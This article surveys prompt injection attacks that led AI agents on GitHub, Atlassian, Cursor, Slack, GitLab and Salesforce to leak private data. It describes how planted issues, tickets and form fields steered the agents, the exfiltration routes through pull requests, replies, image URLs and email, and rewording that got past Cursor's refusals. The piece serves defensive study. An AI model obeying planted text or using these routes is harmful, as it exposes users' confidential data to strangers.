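# Data exfiltration through official tool integrations: GitHub, Supabase, Atlassian and others, 2025 to 2026

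## How an agent reaches company data through an official tool server

Data exfiltration is the unauthorised transfer of private information out of the systems that hold it. Since 2025, security researchers have documented cases of it that involve AI agents. GitHub, Supabase, Atlassian and other companies that store their customers' code, databases and support tickets now publish software that connects a customer's agent to the customer's account. The agent can read a bug report, look something up in a private file and post a reply. It also reads what strangers have written in the same service. A stranger can therefore obtain private data without stealing a password or breaking an access rule. They plant a few sentences in a public bug report or a support form and wait for a customer's agent to read them. The agent may then send back private data, often as a comment or a proposed code change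 in the same service.

### The agent loop, the protocol and the borrowed login

An agent is a language model that works in a loop. Given a task, it chooses a tool call, reads the result, and chooses the next call based on it, until the task is done.

Most of the agents in these cases find their tools through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open standard that Anthropic, the developer of the Claude models, released in November 2024. The US National Security Agency (NSA), in *Model Context Protocol (MCP)* (2026), describes it as the de facto standard for communication between AI-driven services. The application the user works in, such as Claude Desktop or the VS Code editor, is the host. The host runs a separate client for each server it connects to. A server is a program that turns a service's operations into tools a model can call, and an official tool server is one that the company behind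 the service publishes.

The Model Context Protocol's *Tools* specification (2026) describes how a model uses a server's tools. The client requests a list of tools from the server and gets back each tool's name, a plain-language description and the arguments it takes. The model picks one. The client sends the call, the server carries it out, and the result, usually text, goes back to the model. The specification describes tools as "model-controlled", meaning that the model can find and invoke them automatically, based on the context and the user's prompts. Each result becomes input to the model's next decision, and in a service full of public comments and tickets, strangers write much of that input.

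The Model Context Protocol keeps servers apart from one another. Its architecture page lists as a design principle that no server should be able to read the whole conversation or see into another server. But the host combines the results from all servers and passes them to one model, so public and private pages end up in the same context, whether they came from two services or one.

A tool server needs credentials to open the user's account. With a remote server, the user signs in and consents, an authorization service issues an access token, and the client attaches the token to every request. The Model Context Protocol's authorization specification (2025) describes the client as acting "on behalf of resource owners". A server on the user's own machine usually takes its credentials from the local environment. GitHub (2026) lets users of its server either sign in or supply a personal access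 token, a long string that works like a password. Either way, the agent then has the user's authority. The token identifies the account but not whose words led to the call, so a request for a private file looks the same whether it began with the user's question or with a sentence in a stranger's bug report.

An agent's authority depends on its token's scopes, the permissions attached to the token. Under the protocol's authorization rules, a client should request only the scopes it needs. A general-purpose client can rarely determine these in advance, so when a server gives no guidance, the client requests every scope on the server's published list, which server makers are supposed to keep short. The NSA describes the result on GitHub as "blanket access", with tools able to read and write across a user's public and private repositories (project code folders). That description probably fits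 a user who grants every permission once and doesn't revisit the decision. GitHub's documentation recommends minimal permissions and separate tokens for different projects, and a user who follows this advice gives the agent much narrower access.

### Commands and content in one stream

A language model processes a single sequence of text fragments, called tokens, and predicts the next one. That sequence includes the operator's standing instructions, the user's request and, for example, a bug report written by someone else. In *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, the software developer Simon Willison (2025) concludes that models follow instructions in content and cannot reliably rank those instructions by where they came from.

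Older software had a similar weakness, SQL injection, which developers have largely fixed. An attacker types database commands into a web form, and a poorly written program passes them to the database as though its own developer had written them. The remedy is the parameterised query, which sends the command and the user's input separately so that the database never treats the input as a command. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 essay for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, David C argued that language models may never have an equivalent, because they only predict the next token and have no internal separation between commands and data. Developers can train a model to favour its instructions, mark off outside content, or screen for suspicious text. In his account, these measures try to add a distinction that the underlying technology lacks,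 so they make a successful attack less likely but can't rule it out.

In an indirect prompt injection attack, someone with no access to the AI system writes instructions into text that an agent will later read, and the agent follows them as if its user had given them. David C gives the example of a job applicant who hides a line in a CV telling the recruiter's screening model to approve the candidate for interview.

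Once such a model has tools, it becomes what security engineers call a confused deputy, a program that can be tricked into using its legitimate authority for someone who lacks it. Engineers can repair an ordinary confused deputy, but David C considers language models "inherently confusable". He advises designers to assume that some attacks will succeed and to use conventional code to limit what the agent can do afterwards. He also endorses a rule from an exchange on X between Willison and Baibhav Bista, that a model that reads text from some party should drop to that party's privileges. Official tool servers usually don't follow this rule, since the agent keeps the user's full token after reading a stranger's text.

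### The lethal trifecta in three calls

An agent that follows an attacker's instructions can leak private data only if it can both read that data and send it out. In June 2025 Willison named the full combination the lethal trifecta: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and the ability to communicate externally. Untrusted content includes any text that someone other than the agent's user or operator could have written. An agent can communicate externally by loading an image from a web address, showing a link for the user to click, or using a write-back channel, which is a write operation inside the service that puts text where the attacker can read it. Comments, database rows and pull requests (proposed changes to a project's code) can all serve as write-back channels.

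A single official server can be enough for a trifecta attack, which requires access to private data, exposure to outside text and a way to send data out. Willison pointed out in *GitHub MCP Exploited* that GitHub's server "combines all three ingredients in a single package". His original worry was about users who combine them by connecting several servers, and he later observed in *Supabase MCP can leak your entire SQL database* (Willison, 2025) that most trifecta attacks through MCP rely on such combinations.

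In a routine example, a developer asks an agent to handle a GitHub issue (a bug report) about outdated example settings in a public project. The current settings are in a private repository.

| Call | Tool on GitHub's server | What the agent does | Part of the trifecta |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | `issue_read` | Reads the issue in the public repository | Untrusted text |
| 2 | `get_file_contents` | Reads the settings file in the private repository | Private data |
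| 3 | `create_pull_request` | Proposes new example settings in the public repository | Outbound channel |

If the agent carries over only the harmless lines, the developer has saved half an hour. But whoever filed the issue could word it so that the agent copies the entire private file into the public pull request. Only the issue's wording would differ, and the agent would make the same calls in the same order. GitHub's access rules permit each call because the developer is allowed to read the file and open the pull request.

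GitHub's default setup includes the tool groups for repositories, issues and pull requests, so a user who configures nothing gets the tools for all of this. Restricting the server to a few individually chosen tools does not necessarily help, because the example list in GitHub's documentation contains exactly these three tools.

In this trace, a legitimate server relays a stranger's hostile text. A malicious server package is a different problem, because its publisher builds the attack into the tool itself. Vetting the publisher protects only against malicious packages. Atlassian, which makes the ticket tracker Jira, lists the two risks separately in its advice to customers. Its recommendations include giving the agent the least access it needs and having a person approve any action that changes data.

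### Approval prompts and the habit of clicking yes

Human approval is also the protocol's main safeguard. Under the Model Context Protocol specification, a person should always be able to deny a tool call, and clients should display a call's inputs before sending it, to prevent exfiltration. The word "should" makes this a recommendation, and the NSA points out that the protocol cannot enforce it. Some applications follow it anyway, such as Claude Desktop, which by default asks the user to confirm each call. But many users choose "Always Allow" and stop monitoring what the agent does, as Invariant Labs noted in *GitHub MCP Exploited* (2025). A developer who has chosen that option for the pull-request tool gets no chance to stop the third call in the table.

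Users who keep permission prompts on tend to stop reading them, a problem known as approval fatigue. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports that users of the company's coding agent approved 97% of permission prompts. They rejected 39% of the plans the agent presented for approval, so they do push back when a question seems worth reading. In a controlled study, 1,053 paid testers worked on a coding task, and partway through each session a clearly dangerous command replaced the text in one permission prompt. Only 143 testers (13.6%) refused it. The refusal rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts.

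There are reasons to discount these figures somewhat. The testers were not working in their own code, so they had less to lose, and Anthropic was arguing for replacing the prompts. But the command in the study was plainly dangerous. A pull request that leaks a few private lines looks like the work the user asked for, so people would probably catch it even less often.

Anthropic's replacement is an automated classifier that reviews each call and blocks those it rates as risky. It became the default for new Claude Code sessions on most subscription plans in August 2026. It blocked 89% of the same dangerous commands. In a separate evaluation that Anthropic commissioned from the testing company Trajectory Labs, all 720 attempts at indirect prompt injection failed against three Claude models running with the classifier. The models themselves seem to account for most of this result, since attacks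 succeeded only 0.09% of the time on average without the classifier. By contrast, Willison wrote in 2025 that a planted instruction had "a very good chance" of working. However, the evaluation used a browser integration, so it did not test agents reading tickets or issues through a vendor's own server. In an August 2026 post, Willison agreed that the classifier is better than asking people to click OK every few steps, but he still wanted more independent confirmation and pointed to the 11% of dangerous commands that it had let through.

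### Two precursors: Slack AI and GitLab Duo

The technique is older than the official tool servers. Two earlier cases involved assistants that vendors had built into their own products. In both, the stolen data left through the assistant's answer, by way of the victim's browser.

Slack AI answers questions from the messages in a company's Slack workspace. In August 2024, the security firm PromptArmor reported in *Data Exfiltration from Slack AI via Indirect Prompt Injection* that the feature also searched public channels the user had never joined. An attacker with an account in the workspace could create a public channel with no other members and post an instruction there. In the demonstration, a user had stored an API key, a password that programs use, in a private channel and later asked Slack AI for it. The search retrieved both the message containing the key and the attacker's instruction.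 Slack AI then displayed a fake error notice with a link for logging in again. Clicking the link sent the key, which was part of its address, to the attacker's website. The answer cited only the user's private channel, so the victim had little chance of tracing the instruction.

PromptArmor informed Slack on 14 August. Slack replied five days later that the evidence was insufficient and that searching public channels was intended behaviour. This was true of the search but did not address the link. PromptArmor published its report on 20 August, and Slack (2024) deployed a patch the same day. Slack stressed that the attack required narrow conditions, in particular an account in the same workspace, and reported no evidence of unauthorised access to customer data. Its statement gave no details of the patch.

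The second case did not require the user to click anything. GitLab is a code host like GitHub, and Duo is its built-in assistant. Legit Security's *Remote Prompt Injection in GitLab Duo Leads to Source Code Theft*, published on 22 May 2025, showed that Duo responded to instructions hidden in source code, commit messages, issues, and merge requests (GitLab's term for pull requests). An attacker could make the text invisible to people, for example by setting it in white. Duo had the same permissions as the person using it. When a user asked a routine question about a file in a public project, a hidden instruction led Duo to fetch code changes from one of the user's private projects, encode them, and put them in the web address of an image in its answer. When the user's browser tried to load the image, it sent the code to the attacker's server.

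Legit Security had reported this to GitLab on 12 February 2025, and GitLab fixed it before publication. The patch stops Duo from displaying image and form tags that point to domains outside GitLab's own. GitLab told the researchers that it had also fixed the prompt injection, but the change they describe affects only Duo's output. It prevents the browser from leaking data through those tags, but it is unclear whether planted text can still steer the model.

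An agent with a tool server can write to the service directly, so it can leak data without a browser. Four days after the Duo report, Invariant Labs showed the same kind of theft through GitHub's official server, using a pull request instead of an image to carry the data out.

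## May 2025: a public GitHub issue exposes private repositories

For the attack that Invariant Labs published on 26 May 2025, the attacker needed only an ordinary GitHub account. Marco Milanta and Luca Beurer-Kellner of the Zurich company set up a demonstration account with a public repository, `pacman`, containing a simple Pac-Man game, and private repositories containing personal projects and sensitive details about the account's owner. The researchers connected the account to Claude Desktop through GitHub's official server, using Claude 4 Opus, then one of Anthropic's newest models.

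### From a fan's suggestion to a public pull request

Anyone on GitHub can file an issue in a public repository. The planted issue looked like a suggestion from an admirer, who praised the game and said its author deserved to be better known. It asked for a list of the author's other projects and a new passage about the author in the README (the page that introduces a project), based on the READMEs in all of the author's repositories. It also claimed that the author did not care about privacy. Any visitor could read the issue's text, unlike the invisible text in the GitLab Duo attack.

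Invariant Labs recorded the owner's request as "Have a look at issues in my open source repo pacman and address them!" *Securing MCP-based Agent Workflows*, Grigoris Ntousakis's 2026 master's thesis at Brown University, reconstructs the tool calls that followed. The agent first called `list_issues`, which returned the planted text along with any genuine reports. It then called `list_repositories` to find every repository it could open, and `get_file_contents` to read the README in each. One private README contained personal information, which the agent copied into the public project's README using `create_or_update_file`.

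In Invariant's demonstration, the change was a pull request that disclosed the name of a private repository, Jupiter Star, and the owner's salary and plan to move to South America. The owner did not have to accept the change for the data to leak. The German technology site heise pointed out in *Attack via GitHub MCP server* that the information never reached the README, but everyone could see the pull request.

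The owner told the agent to "address them", which meant carrying out the requests in the issues. A passage about the author is a plausible request, so the agent had to recognise that this one went beyond anything the owner would want. An owner who only asks for a summary does not authorise the agent to act on the issues. Willison wrote that asking Claude to look at the issues was enough to set off the leak, but the recorded request went further.

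### Toxic agent flows

Invariant Labs named this pattern a toxic agent flow, in which an indirect prompt injection triggers a harmful sequence of tool calls. The harm comes from the sequence, because every tool in the demonstration was genuine and each call was ordinary on its own.

Invariant Labs said that its automated scanner had found the flow, and it explained the method two months later. An agent can use its tools in any combination, so a security review has to consider every possible subset, and a set of 30 tools has more than a billion. The framework described in Invariant Labs (2025) models the possible sequences of tools as a graph. It labels how far each tool's output can be trusted, how sensitive the data is, and whether the tool could send data out. It then looks for paths that run from untrusted text through private data to a tool that can send data out, and scores them. GitHub's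 server has such a path on its own. Such a scan can find a dangerous path before anyone exploits it, but it doesn't measure how often a given model would follow a stranger's instructions along that path.

Milanta and Beurer-Kellner wrote that the server's code had no flaw and that GitHub alone could not solve the problem with server-side patches. They called it an architectural problem that developers must address in the agent system as a whole. Their argument is a good one because the server cannot distinguish a call prompted by the user from one prompted by a stranger's issue.

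The claim is too strong if it means that GitHub could do nothing useful. GitHub can't make someone else's model distinguish its user from a stranger, but it decides what text its server returns and which changes the server accepts. On 27 May the developer news site DevClass reported in *Researchers warn of prompt injection vulnerability in GitHub MCP* that someone had already proposed an optional server filter that would show the agent only text by people with push access, the right to change a repository's code directly. DevClass found the idea interesting but crude, since it would also hide many useful contributions. GitHub (2025) introduced a similar setting, lockdown mode, that December. If the owner had switched it on, it would have withheld a stranger's issue from the agent.

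### One repository per session

Invariant Labs' main proposal was a rule that limits an agent to one repository per session. The rule runs in Guardrails, the company's own product, and is enforced by a proxy, a program that all calls between the agent and its tools pass through. The proxy compares the repository name and owner in any two repository actions in a session and raises a violation if either differs. It checks the owner because two accounts can each have a repository with the same name.

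In the `pacman` case, the agent begins by listing that repository's issues. When it later tries to read the README of a private project, the repository name in the call no longer matches, and the proxy blocks the call. The block doesn't depend on what the issue says, so an attacker can't avoid it by rewording the text.

Docker, which makes software for running programs in isolated containers, built a simpler version. The script in its *MCP Horror Stories* (2025) records the first repository an agent opens and blocks calls to any other. Docker tested the script with two direct calls: a read from a public repository succeeded, and a read from a private one returned a security error. The test didn't include a language model or a planted issue, but this matters less than it might seem, because the script applies the same rule regardless of why the model made a call.

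Docker also said that the script makes Invariant's attack "impossible", which is harder to accept. A call that lists a user's repositories doesn't name any single repository, so a rule that only compares names doesn't apply to it. Unless the rule's author handles listing and search tools separately, the agent could still obtain the names of private projects, such as Jupiter Star, and publish them in `pacman`. The salary and travel plans would be safe, but project names can themselves be sensitive if they refer to an unannounced product or a client.

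The rule also blocks much legitimate work. A developer can't ask an agent to update public example settings from a private configuration file, or to change a shared library and then repair the applications that depend on it if they are in separate repositories. Even sorting the bug reports of two public projects in one session breaks the rule, although there is nothing private to leak. Invariant's claim that the rule maintains "full functionality within authorized boundaries" is true only of tasks that fit inside one repository. For anything else, the developer has to start a new session and carry the results across by hand.

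Ntousakis proposed a less restrictive test, based on whether a repository is public or private. His system, SAMOS, also sits between the agent and its tools. Once the agent has read an issue in a public repository, SAMOS marks the session as public and blocks the agent from opening private repositories. An agent could work on several public projects at once. It still could not bring the private settings into the public example, because that task and the theft both move data from a private repository to a public one.

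SAMOS depends on someone labelling each tool as confidential or not, but GitHub's `get_file_contents` reads both public and private repositories. Ntousakis suggests either that the tool report whether the repository is public or private with each result, or that developers split it into two tools, one for each kind. His thesis describes how SAMOS would block the GitHub attack but names no model and gives no success rate, so it adds little evidence about how often the attack works.

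### A token that opens only one repository

In a Hacker News thread about Invariant Labs' post, an early commenter objected that the attack needed an unusually powerful credential. GitHub users can limit a fine-grained access token to chosen repositories. Had the owner given Claude a token for `pacman` alone, Claude could not have read the private files, even if it had followed the instructions in the planted issue.

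This is correct, and the token is the stronger control for this attack. GitHub itself enforces the token's limit, so it holds even if the agent bypasses the proxy or uses a tool the rule's author forgot.

| The agent's call | One repository per session | Token limited to `pacman` |
|---|---|---|
| List the issues in `pacman` | Goes through | Goes through |
| List the owner's repositories | Goes through unless the rule covers listing tools | Returns no private repositories |
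| Read a private README | The proxy blocks it | GitHub refuses it |
| Open a pull request in `pacman` | Goes through, possibly with private project names | Goes through, with nothing from private repositories |

With the session rule, an agent can work on `pacman` in one session and Jupiter Star in the next, using the same login. With a restricted token, the user has to choose the repositories in advance and change or switch tokens for each new job. Someone who tires of this and adds Jupiter Star to the `pacman` token recreates the conditions for the attack. Both limits block the same legitimate tasks, because an agent that cannot read the private settings cannot copy the harmless lines from them.

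Beurer-Kellner accepted in the thread that overly broad tokens were part of the problem. He said people want general agents they don't have to unlock one repository at a time, so they hand over broad tokens and trust the model. One commenter could imagine a user looking at GitHub's 20 to 30 separate permissions, giving up, and creating an old-style token with access to everything. Another said they had done this after failing to find the right combination of permissions.

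Even careful users had trouble limiting an agent's access. Josh Mandel wrote that he had created a second GitHub account for Jules, Google's coding agent, because Jules had asked for access to all his repositories and he saw no other safe way to use it. Another commenter pointed him to a settings page where he could restrict Jules to a list of repositories. These anecdotes come from a self-selected group, but they suggest that broad tokens are a common choice. Docker likewise reported that setup instructions usually lead developers to use a single token that covers every repository they can open.

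### The weight of a single demonstration

Invariant Labs showed that a leak of this kind was possible with a leading model and GitHub's own server. The company linked to the full record of the session, and the issue and the pull request were public, so readers could check what happened. The attack's success rate is much less clear, because Invariant did not report how many times the researchers tried it or how many versions of the issue they wrote. A model can respond differently to the same text on different runs, so one success does not show how often the attack would work.

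The researchers also assumed that the user had chosen "Always Allow" in Claude Desktop. Without that setting, approval prompts would have given the user a chance to refuse a call to read a private file with no obvious connection to a Pac-Man bug. The assumption is fair for many users, but the demonstration does not measure how many. DevClass called the example "contrived". heise thought it relied on a certain recklessness, but that such recklessness was probably not far-fetched.

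Invariant's researchers made some broader claims that they did not demonstrate. They wrote that the vulnerability affected any agent using GitHub's server, whatever its model. Any such agent could make the same calls if its token allowed them, but the researchers reported results for only one model, so they did not show that others would follow the instructions in the issue. They also said that many off-the-shelf prompt injection detectors miss the attack. This is plausible, since the planted text resembled an ordinary feature request, but readers cannot check it because the researchers named no detectors and gave no figures.

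Invariant had a commercial interest in the threat it described. In its post, the company recommended its own Guardrails and MCP-scan software and invited readers to join an early-access programme. Four weeks later the security company Snyk bought Invariant, which had been spun off from the university ETH Zurich in 2024, according to SiliconANGLE's *Snyk acquires Invariant Labs to expand AI agent security capabilities* (2025). Invariant's commercial interest is a reason to be cautious about how urgent the threat was and whether specialised software was the best remedy. It has less bearing on whether the leak occurred, because anyone could see the leak in the pull request.

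The victim was the researchers' own demonstration account, but later retellings made the case sound worse. Docker introduced it as one of a series of "real incidents" in which hackers had broken into companies. Tessl, which makes tools for AI-assisted programming, wrote in its account of the disclosure that there was no known active attack of this kind. That had changed somewhat by June 2026, as Microsoft (2026) had observed prompt injection attempts in public repositories whose automated workflows used AI agents.

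### GitHub's silence and the later tests

GitHub seems to have made no public statement about the disclosure at the time. DevClass and heise reported none, and the developer akhilesharora, in *Exfil through an approved tool*, looked for one and found nothing. He also noted that the case had no CVE, the public identifier that security scanners use to flag software with a known vulnerability. He writes that a community member filed a reproduction of the attack with the server's maintainers in August 2025, as issue 844, and that it went stale without an official reply. No other source confirms this, and he does not describe the model or the result in detail.

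That same month, GitHub began checking the server's calls involving public repositories for passwords and other secrets. The check would not have caught this leak, because the leaked details were a salary and a plan to emigrate, not credentials.

GitHub's *Safeguarding VS Code against prompt injections*, which GitHub Security Lab (2025) announced on 25 August, describes a closely related attack. A GitHub researcher planted instructions in issues and asked the Copilot agent in the VS Code editor about them. One issue led GPT-4o to read a GitHub token from a file on the user's computer and send it to an outside website. The user had asked only for details about the issue, whereas in Invariant's demonstration the owner had told the agent to act on what it read.

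The researcher also found that tool call results could mislead GPT-4.1, Gemini 2.5 Pro and Claude Sonnet 4. The models often ignored the planted instructions at first, so he had to add tricks such as a condition that happened to be true or an imitation of the agent's standing instructions. Claude Sonnet 4 seemed the most resistant, but he could still trick it reliably. Because GitHub had no commercial reason to exaggerate the problem, these findings are good support for Invariant's central point, but they don't reproduce its exact attack. VS Code always asked for approval before it ran a tool from an MCP server, so the researcher looked for built-in tools that could send data out without asking. GitHub and the VS Code team have since closed the gaps he described.

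No one appears to have published a rerun of the `pacman` attack on 2026 models. The closest evidence is from *GitInject* (2026), which tested agents in automated GitHub workflows and found that frontier models increasingly resist direct instructions in an issue. An issue disguised as a security audit failed to get an access token from a Claude-based workflow or a Gemini-based one. But when an issue presented its request as a routine diagnostic, the coding agent Cline listed the owner's private repositories in a reply visible to anyone who could read the issue. Invariant's leak also listed private repositories, which exposed Jupiter Star, but it included private files as well. In July 2026, Noma Security demonstrated an attack on GitHub's own Agentic Workflows that again leaked the contents of private repositories through a public issue, according to mcp.directory's *GitLost*.

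## From June 2025: support desks and public forms as the way in

From June 2025, researchers used intake points to steer agents that worked for support engineers, developers and sales staff. An intake point is a form, queue or endpoint through which outsiders can place text in a company's systems. Many companies have no public GitHub repository, but nearly all of them have a support address or a contact form. A less obvious example is Sentry, an error-tracking service that accepts error reports from anyone who copies a key its customers publish in their websites.

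### Why queues suit this attack

An attacker who plants an issue on GitHub depends on the owner assigning an agent to it. At a helpdesk, somebody has to read every ticket, because any ticket could come from a paying customer whose system is down. The work is repetitive and mostly reading and writing short texts, so companies have good reason to give it to an agent.

The person who reads a ticket usually has far more access than the person who wrote it. A customer can see their own tickets, but the engineer who answers may also be able to open other customers' tickets, internal documentation and the company's bug tracker. An agent that uses the engineer's login can open anything the engineer can.

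Planted text can also stay in place until someone opens the ticket, so the attacker doesn't need to know which employee will do so, or when. *Один вредоносный лид против всей CRM* (Antipov, 2026), written for a Russian security news site, describes an attack on Salesforce in which the planted record stayed in the customer database. Every new question about that record gave the instructions another chance to work.

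Many companies also copy requests from Zendesk, a helpdesk product, into Jira, where their developers work. A stranger's email can then appear on a developer's internal task list with little to show where it came from.

Intake points are easy to find. *Pwn the Enterprise*, a newsletter post that accompanied a talk by the security company Zenity at the Black Hat conference in August 2025, reports that Google searches turned up hundreds of mailboxes that automatically create Jira tickets. Similar searches found hundreds of web forms that create support cases in Salesforce. Strangers can write to these mailboxes and forms, but they can't tell where an attack would succeed, because they don't know whether an agent will read the ticket, what the agent can access or whether it can reply. Sending a ticket takes little effort, though, so an attacker could try all of them.

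### Cato's ticket in Jira Service Management

Atlassian launched its official tool server in May 2025. On 19 June, Waizel, Attiya and Bamberger (2025), in *PoC Attack Targeting Atlassian’s Model Context Protocol (MCP)*, showed how someone could attack a company through this server by submitting a support ticket. The three researchers, who work for the network security company Cato Networks, targeted Jira Service Management, Atlassian's helpdesk product. Customers submit requests through its web portal, and staff answer them in Jira.

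In the demonstration, an outside attacker submitted a ticket containing instructions. A support engineer then used Claude Sonnet, connected to Atlassian's server, to process the ticket. The agent followed the instructions with the engineer's permissions, collecting internal data that the attacker had no right to see and writing it into the ticket, where the attacker could read it. The engineer's agent made all the calls to Atlassian's server, so the attacker never connected to it.

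This leak is harder to notice than the one Invariant Labs had shown on GitHub three weeks earlier, which exposed the owner's salary in a pull request anyone could see. A reply to a ticket is normally visible only to the customer and the support staff, and writing replies is a support agent's job.

Atlassian had advertised its server as "keeping data secure and within permissioned boundaries". Willison (2025) quoted that line on the day of the disclosure in *PoC Attack Targeting Atlassian’s Model Context Protocol (MCP)*, a blog post with the same title as Cato's report. In a narrow sense the claim held true in the demonstration, because the agent, like the one in the GitHub attack, did only what its user was allowed to do.

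Cato published a video of the attack working, which is good evidence that it can happen. The company did not report how many attempts it needed, so the success rate is unknown, as it is for Invariant's demonstration. Cato also did not report which version of Claude Sonnet it used or whether the engineer approved each call. It described the stolen material only as internal data from the tenant, the victim company's Atlassian workspace.

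Cato's researchers noted that a Google search reveals many companies' service portals and said that attackers could target them, but they did not test any of these companies. They also described a longer, hypothetical attack through a business partner. An attacker takes over the partner's email account and submits an enhancement request. When a product manager uses an agent to answer it, text planted in the request makes the agent comment on every open Jira issue with a link to a fake documentation page. A tester clicks the link the next day, and the attacker's malware installs itself and steals the tester's passwords.

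The first half of Cato's scenario is believable, since commenting on many issues takes the same permission as commenting on one. The second half needs more than Cato described, because opening a web page doesn't normally install malware. The attacker would also need a flaw in the tester's browser or a further mistake by the tester.

It is also a little unclear how anonymous the attacker can be. Cato wrote that attackers could gain privileged access "without ever authenticating", and Infosecurity Magazine's *Researchers Warn of 'Living off AI' Attacks* describes the outsider as anonymous. Some companies open their portal to everyone, while others require a customer account. Either way, the attacker does not need the staff login that would normally protect the data.

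Cato recommended a rule that blocks tool calls that create, add or edit anything, or at least raises an alert, and it sells a product that enforces such rules. Blocking these calls would have stopped this leak because the agent could not have written to the ticket. But the support engineer's agent could then summarise a ticket without being able to answer it or open a bug report for the developers.

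Willison suggested a narrower rule, that a person must confirm any reply an attacker could see. This suits a helpdesk fairly well because Jira Service Management separates internal notes from replies to the customer, so an agent could write notes freely and wait for approval only before a reply. Support staff also have other reasons to check what they send customers, so they may read these prompts more carefully than developers do. But a busy team would still approve many replies a day, and a few lines from another customer's ticket might not look out of place.

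Cato's report mentions no response from Atlassian. Willison could not tell whether the company had fixed anything, and he doubted that it could, because he considers any server that combines the whole trifecta "insecure by design". In the summer of 2026, other researchers attacked Rovo, Atlassian's built-in assistant.

### From a support email to a developer's computer

In the next disclosure, the reader of the malicious ticket was Cursor, a code editor with a built-in agent. Developers can connect Cursor to Jira so that it looks up the tickets assigned to them. Zenity Labs' *AgentFlayer*, published on 1 August 2025, describes how the researcher Marina Simakov used a Jira ticket to make Cursor leak passwords and keys. In the scenario, the attacker emails a support address, Zendesk turns the email into a ticket, and an automatic sync copies the ticket into Jira. A developer later asks Cursor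 to deal with it.

Simakov's first ticket asked for API keys outright. Cursor refused, saying the request went against good security practice. She then rewrote the ticket to ask for "apples", which she described in a way that matched a common type of login token. Cursor found such a token in the project's files and leaked it.

Cursor refused the first ticket because of what it asked for, but accepted the second, which made the same request in words that no longer sounded like theft. It seems to have ignored that the request came from a ticket rather than the developer. A model that judges requests by how dangerous they sound will stop careless attackers, but an attacker who can keep submitting tickets can reword the request each time.

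In another test, Simakov placed dummy credentials for Amazon's cloud service in a folder outside the project. Cursor refused several times but complied when she encoded the instructions, presented them as help with troubleshooting and again used a harmless word for the credentials. The agent read the file even though a setting meant to protect files outside the project was on. Simakov had switched off auto-run, the mode in which Cursor acts without asking, so the agent stopped before sending the credentials. She wrote that with auto-run on, it would have sent them automatically. This is likely, but she did not carry the theft through as she had with the token.

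Zenity called this a "0click" attack because the victim doesn't have to click a link. The developer still has to direct Cursor to the ticket, and the data can leave without approval only if auto-run is on. Simakov said auto-run is a common choice because approving every call is exhausting, but gave no figures.

Cursor could post the data as a comment on the Jira ticket, which a two-way sync might then carry back to Zendesk and to the attacker. It could also use its own built-in tools to send the data to the attacker's website in a web request. Cato's rule against write calls would not have stopped the web request, which doesn't pass through the Jira server.

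Snyk's security scanner, MCP-Scan, had the same gap. Snyk Labs (2025) acknowledged that the scanner would have missed the attack because it checked only the servers a user had installed and ignored the tools built into the editor. Snyk extended it to cover built-in tools on 20 August. A company that reviews its tool servers one at a time can miss such an attack for the same reason.

Simakov did not say whether the Jira server was Atlassian's own. This makes little difference to the attack, which only needed the server to return the text of a ticket.

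Zenity reported the problem to Cursor on 27 June, and Cursor replied three days later that it was a known issue. It advised users to connect only to servers "that access trusted content" and to list sensitive files that the agent should ignore in a `.cursorignore` file. Under the first recommendation, a company whose Jira receives customers' emails could not connect it to Cursor, and this was the situation Zenity had described. The second covers secrets stored in a project, so it doesn't obviously protect credentials kept elsewhere on the computer. Cursor announced no change to its product, and Zenity recorded the report as closed.

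Zenity advised companies to find out which of their connected sources can contain text from outside, and to turn off auto-run except in environments they have specifically approved.

### Sales forms and Salesforce's agents

Salesforce sells customer relationship management (CRM) software, a database where companies keep their contacts, deals and support cases. Two of its standard features let the public add records to this database. Web-to-Case turns a form submission on a company's website into a support case, and Web-to-Lead turns one into a lead, the record of a potential customer. Salesforce also sells the agents that read these records, first under the name Einstein and more recently as Agentforce. In all the Salesforce attacks, Salesforce therefore supplied the form, the database and the agent.

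Zenity showed the first of them in the same August 2025 talk. An attacker submitted cases containing planted text through a Web-to-Case form. When a sales representative asked Einstein about open cases, the text led it to change the email addresses of the company's contacts. According to The Decoder's *Agent-based AI systems face growing threats from zero-click and one-click exploits*, the new addresses were at a domain the attacker controlled, and each contained the original address in encoded form so the attacker could identify each message's intended recipient.

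In this attack, the company's employees would send private data out themselves whenever they wrote to a customer, so Einstein didn't have to. Checking the agent's answers would have found nothing, because the damage came from an edit to a database record. The attack worked only against companies that had enabled a particular action from Salesforce's library. Salesforce closed Zenity's report without giving a date for a fix, but later confirmed that it had fixed the flaw on 11 July.

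A better-known attack followed in September. Noma Security, which sells protection for AI agents, called it ForcedLeak. Noma put its instructions in the description field of a Salesforce Web-to-Lead form, which SecurityWeek's *Salesforce AI Hack Enabled CRM Data Theft* describes as a form that conference attendees might fill in. ThaiCERT's *ForcedLeak Vulnerability in Salesforce Agentforce Risks CRM Data Exposure via Prompt Injection* (2025) gives the field's limit as roughly 42,000 characters, enough for a long set of instructions with harmless text around them.

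The planted text took effect only when an employee asked Agentforce about the new lead. It was a short list of questions, some trivial, that included a request for the email addresses of the company's other leads. The answer was then sent out in the web address of an image, as the source code was in the GitLab Duo attack.

Willison notes in *ForcedLeak* that Salesforce had a defence against this, a content security rule that limited the sites from which the page could load images. It failed because one of the approved domains had expired, so anyone could register it and receive whatever the browser sent there.

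Noma reported the flaw on 28 July 2025 and rated its severity 9.4 out of 10, according to The Hacker News (2025). Hackread's *ForcedLeak Flaw in Salesforce Agentforce AI Agent Exposed CRM Data* reports that by 8 September Salesforce had taken back the expired domain and begun to enforce Trusted URLs, a list of web addresses to which its agents may send output. Noma disclosed the flaw publicly on 25 September. Companies were also advised to audit their existing leads for unusual submissions, which was sensible because a patch doesn't remove instructions already in the database.

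The patch closed the route by which the data left, but a form submission could still steer the agent. The next two attacks through the same kind of form used other routes.

Capsule Security, another company that sells protection for agents, published one of them, PipeLeak, in April 2026. CSO Online's *Copilot and Agentforce fall to form-based prompt injection tricks* (2026) describes how text in a public lead form led Agentforce to email customer records out in bulk. A list of trusted web addresses does not stop data sent by email. According to Claw Times, Salesforce said it had "remediated the specific scenario described" and now required a person to confirm an agent's email actions by default.

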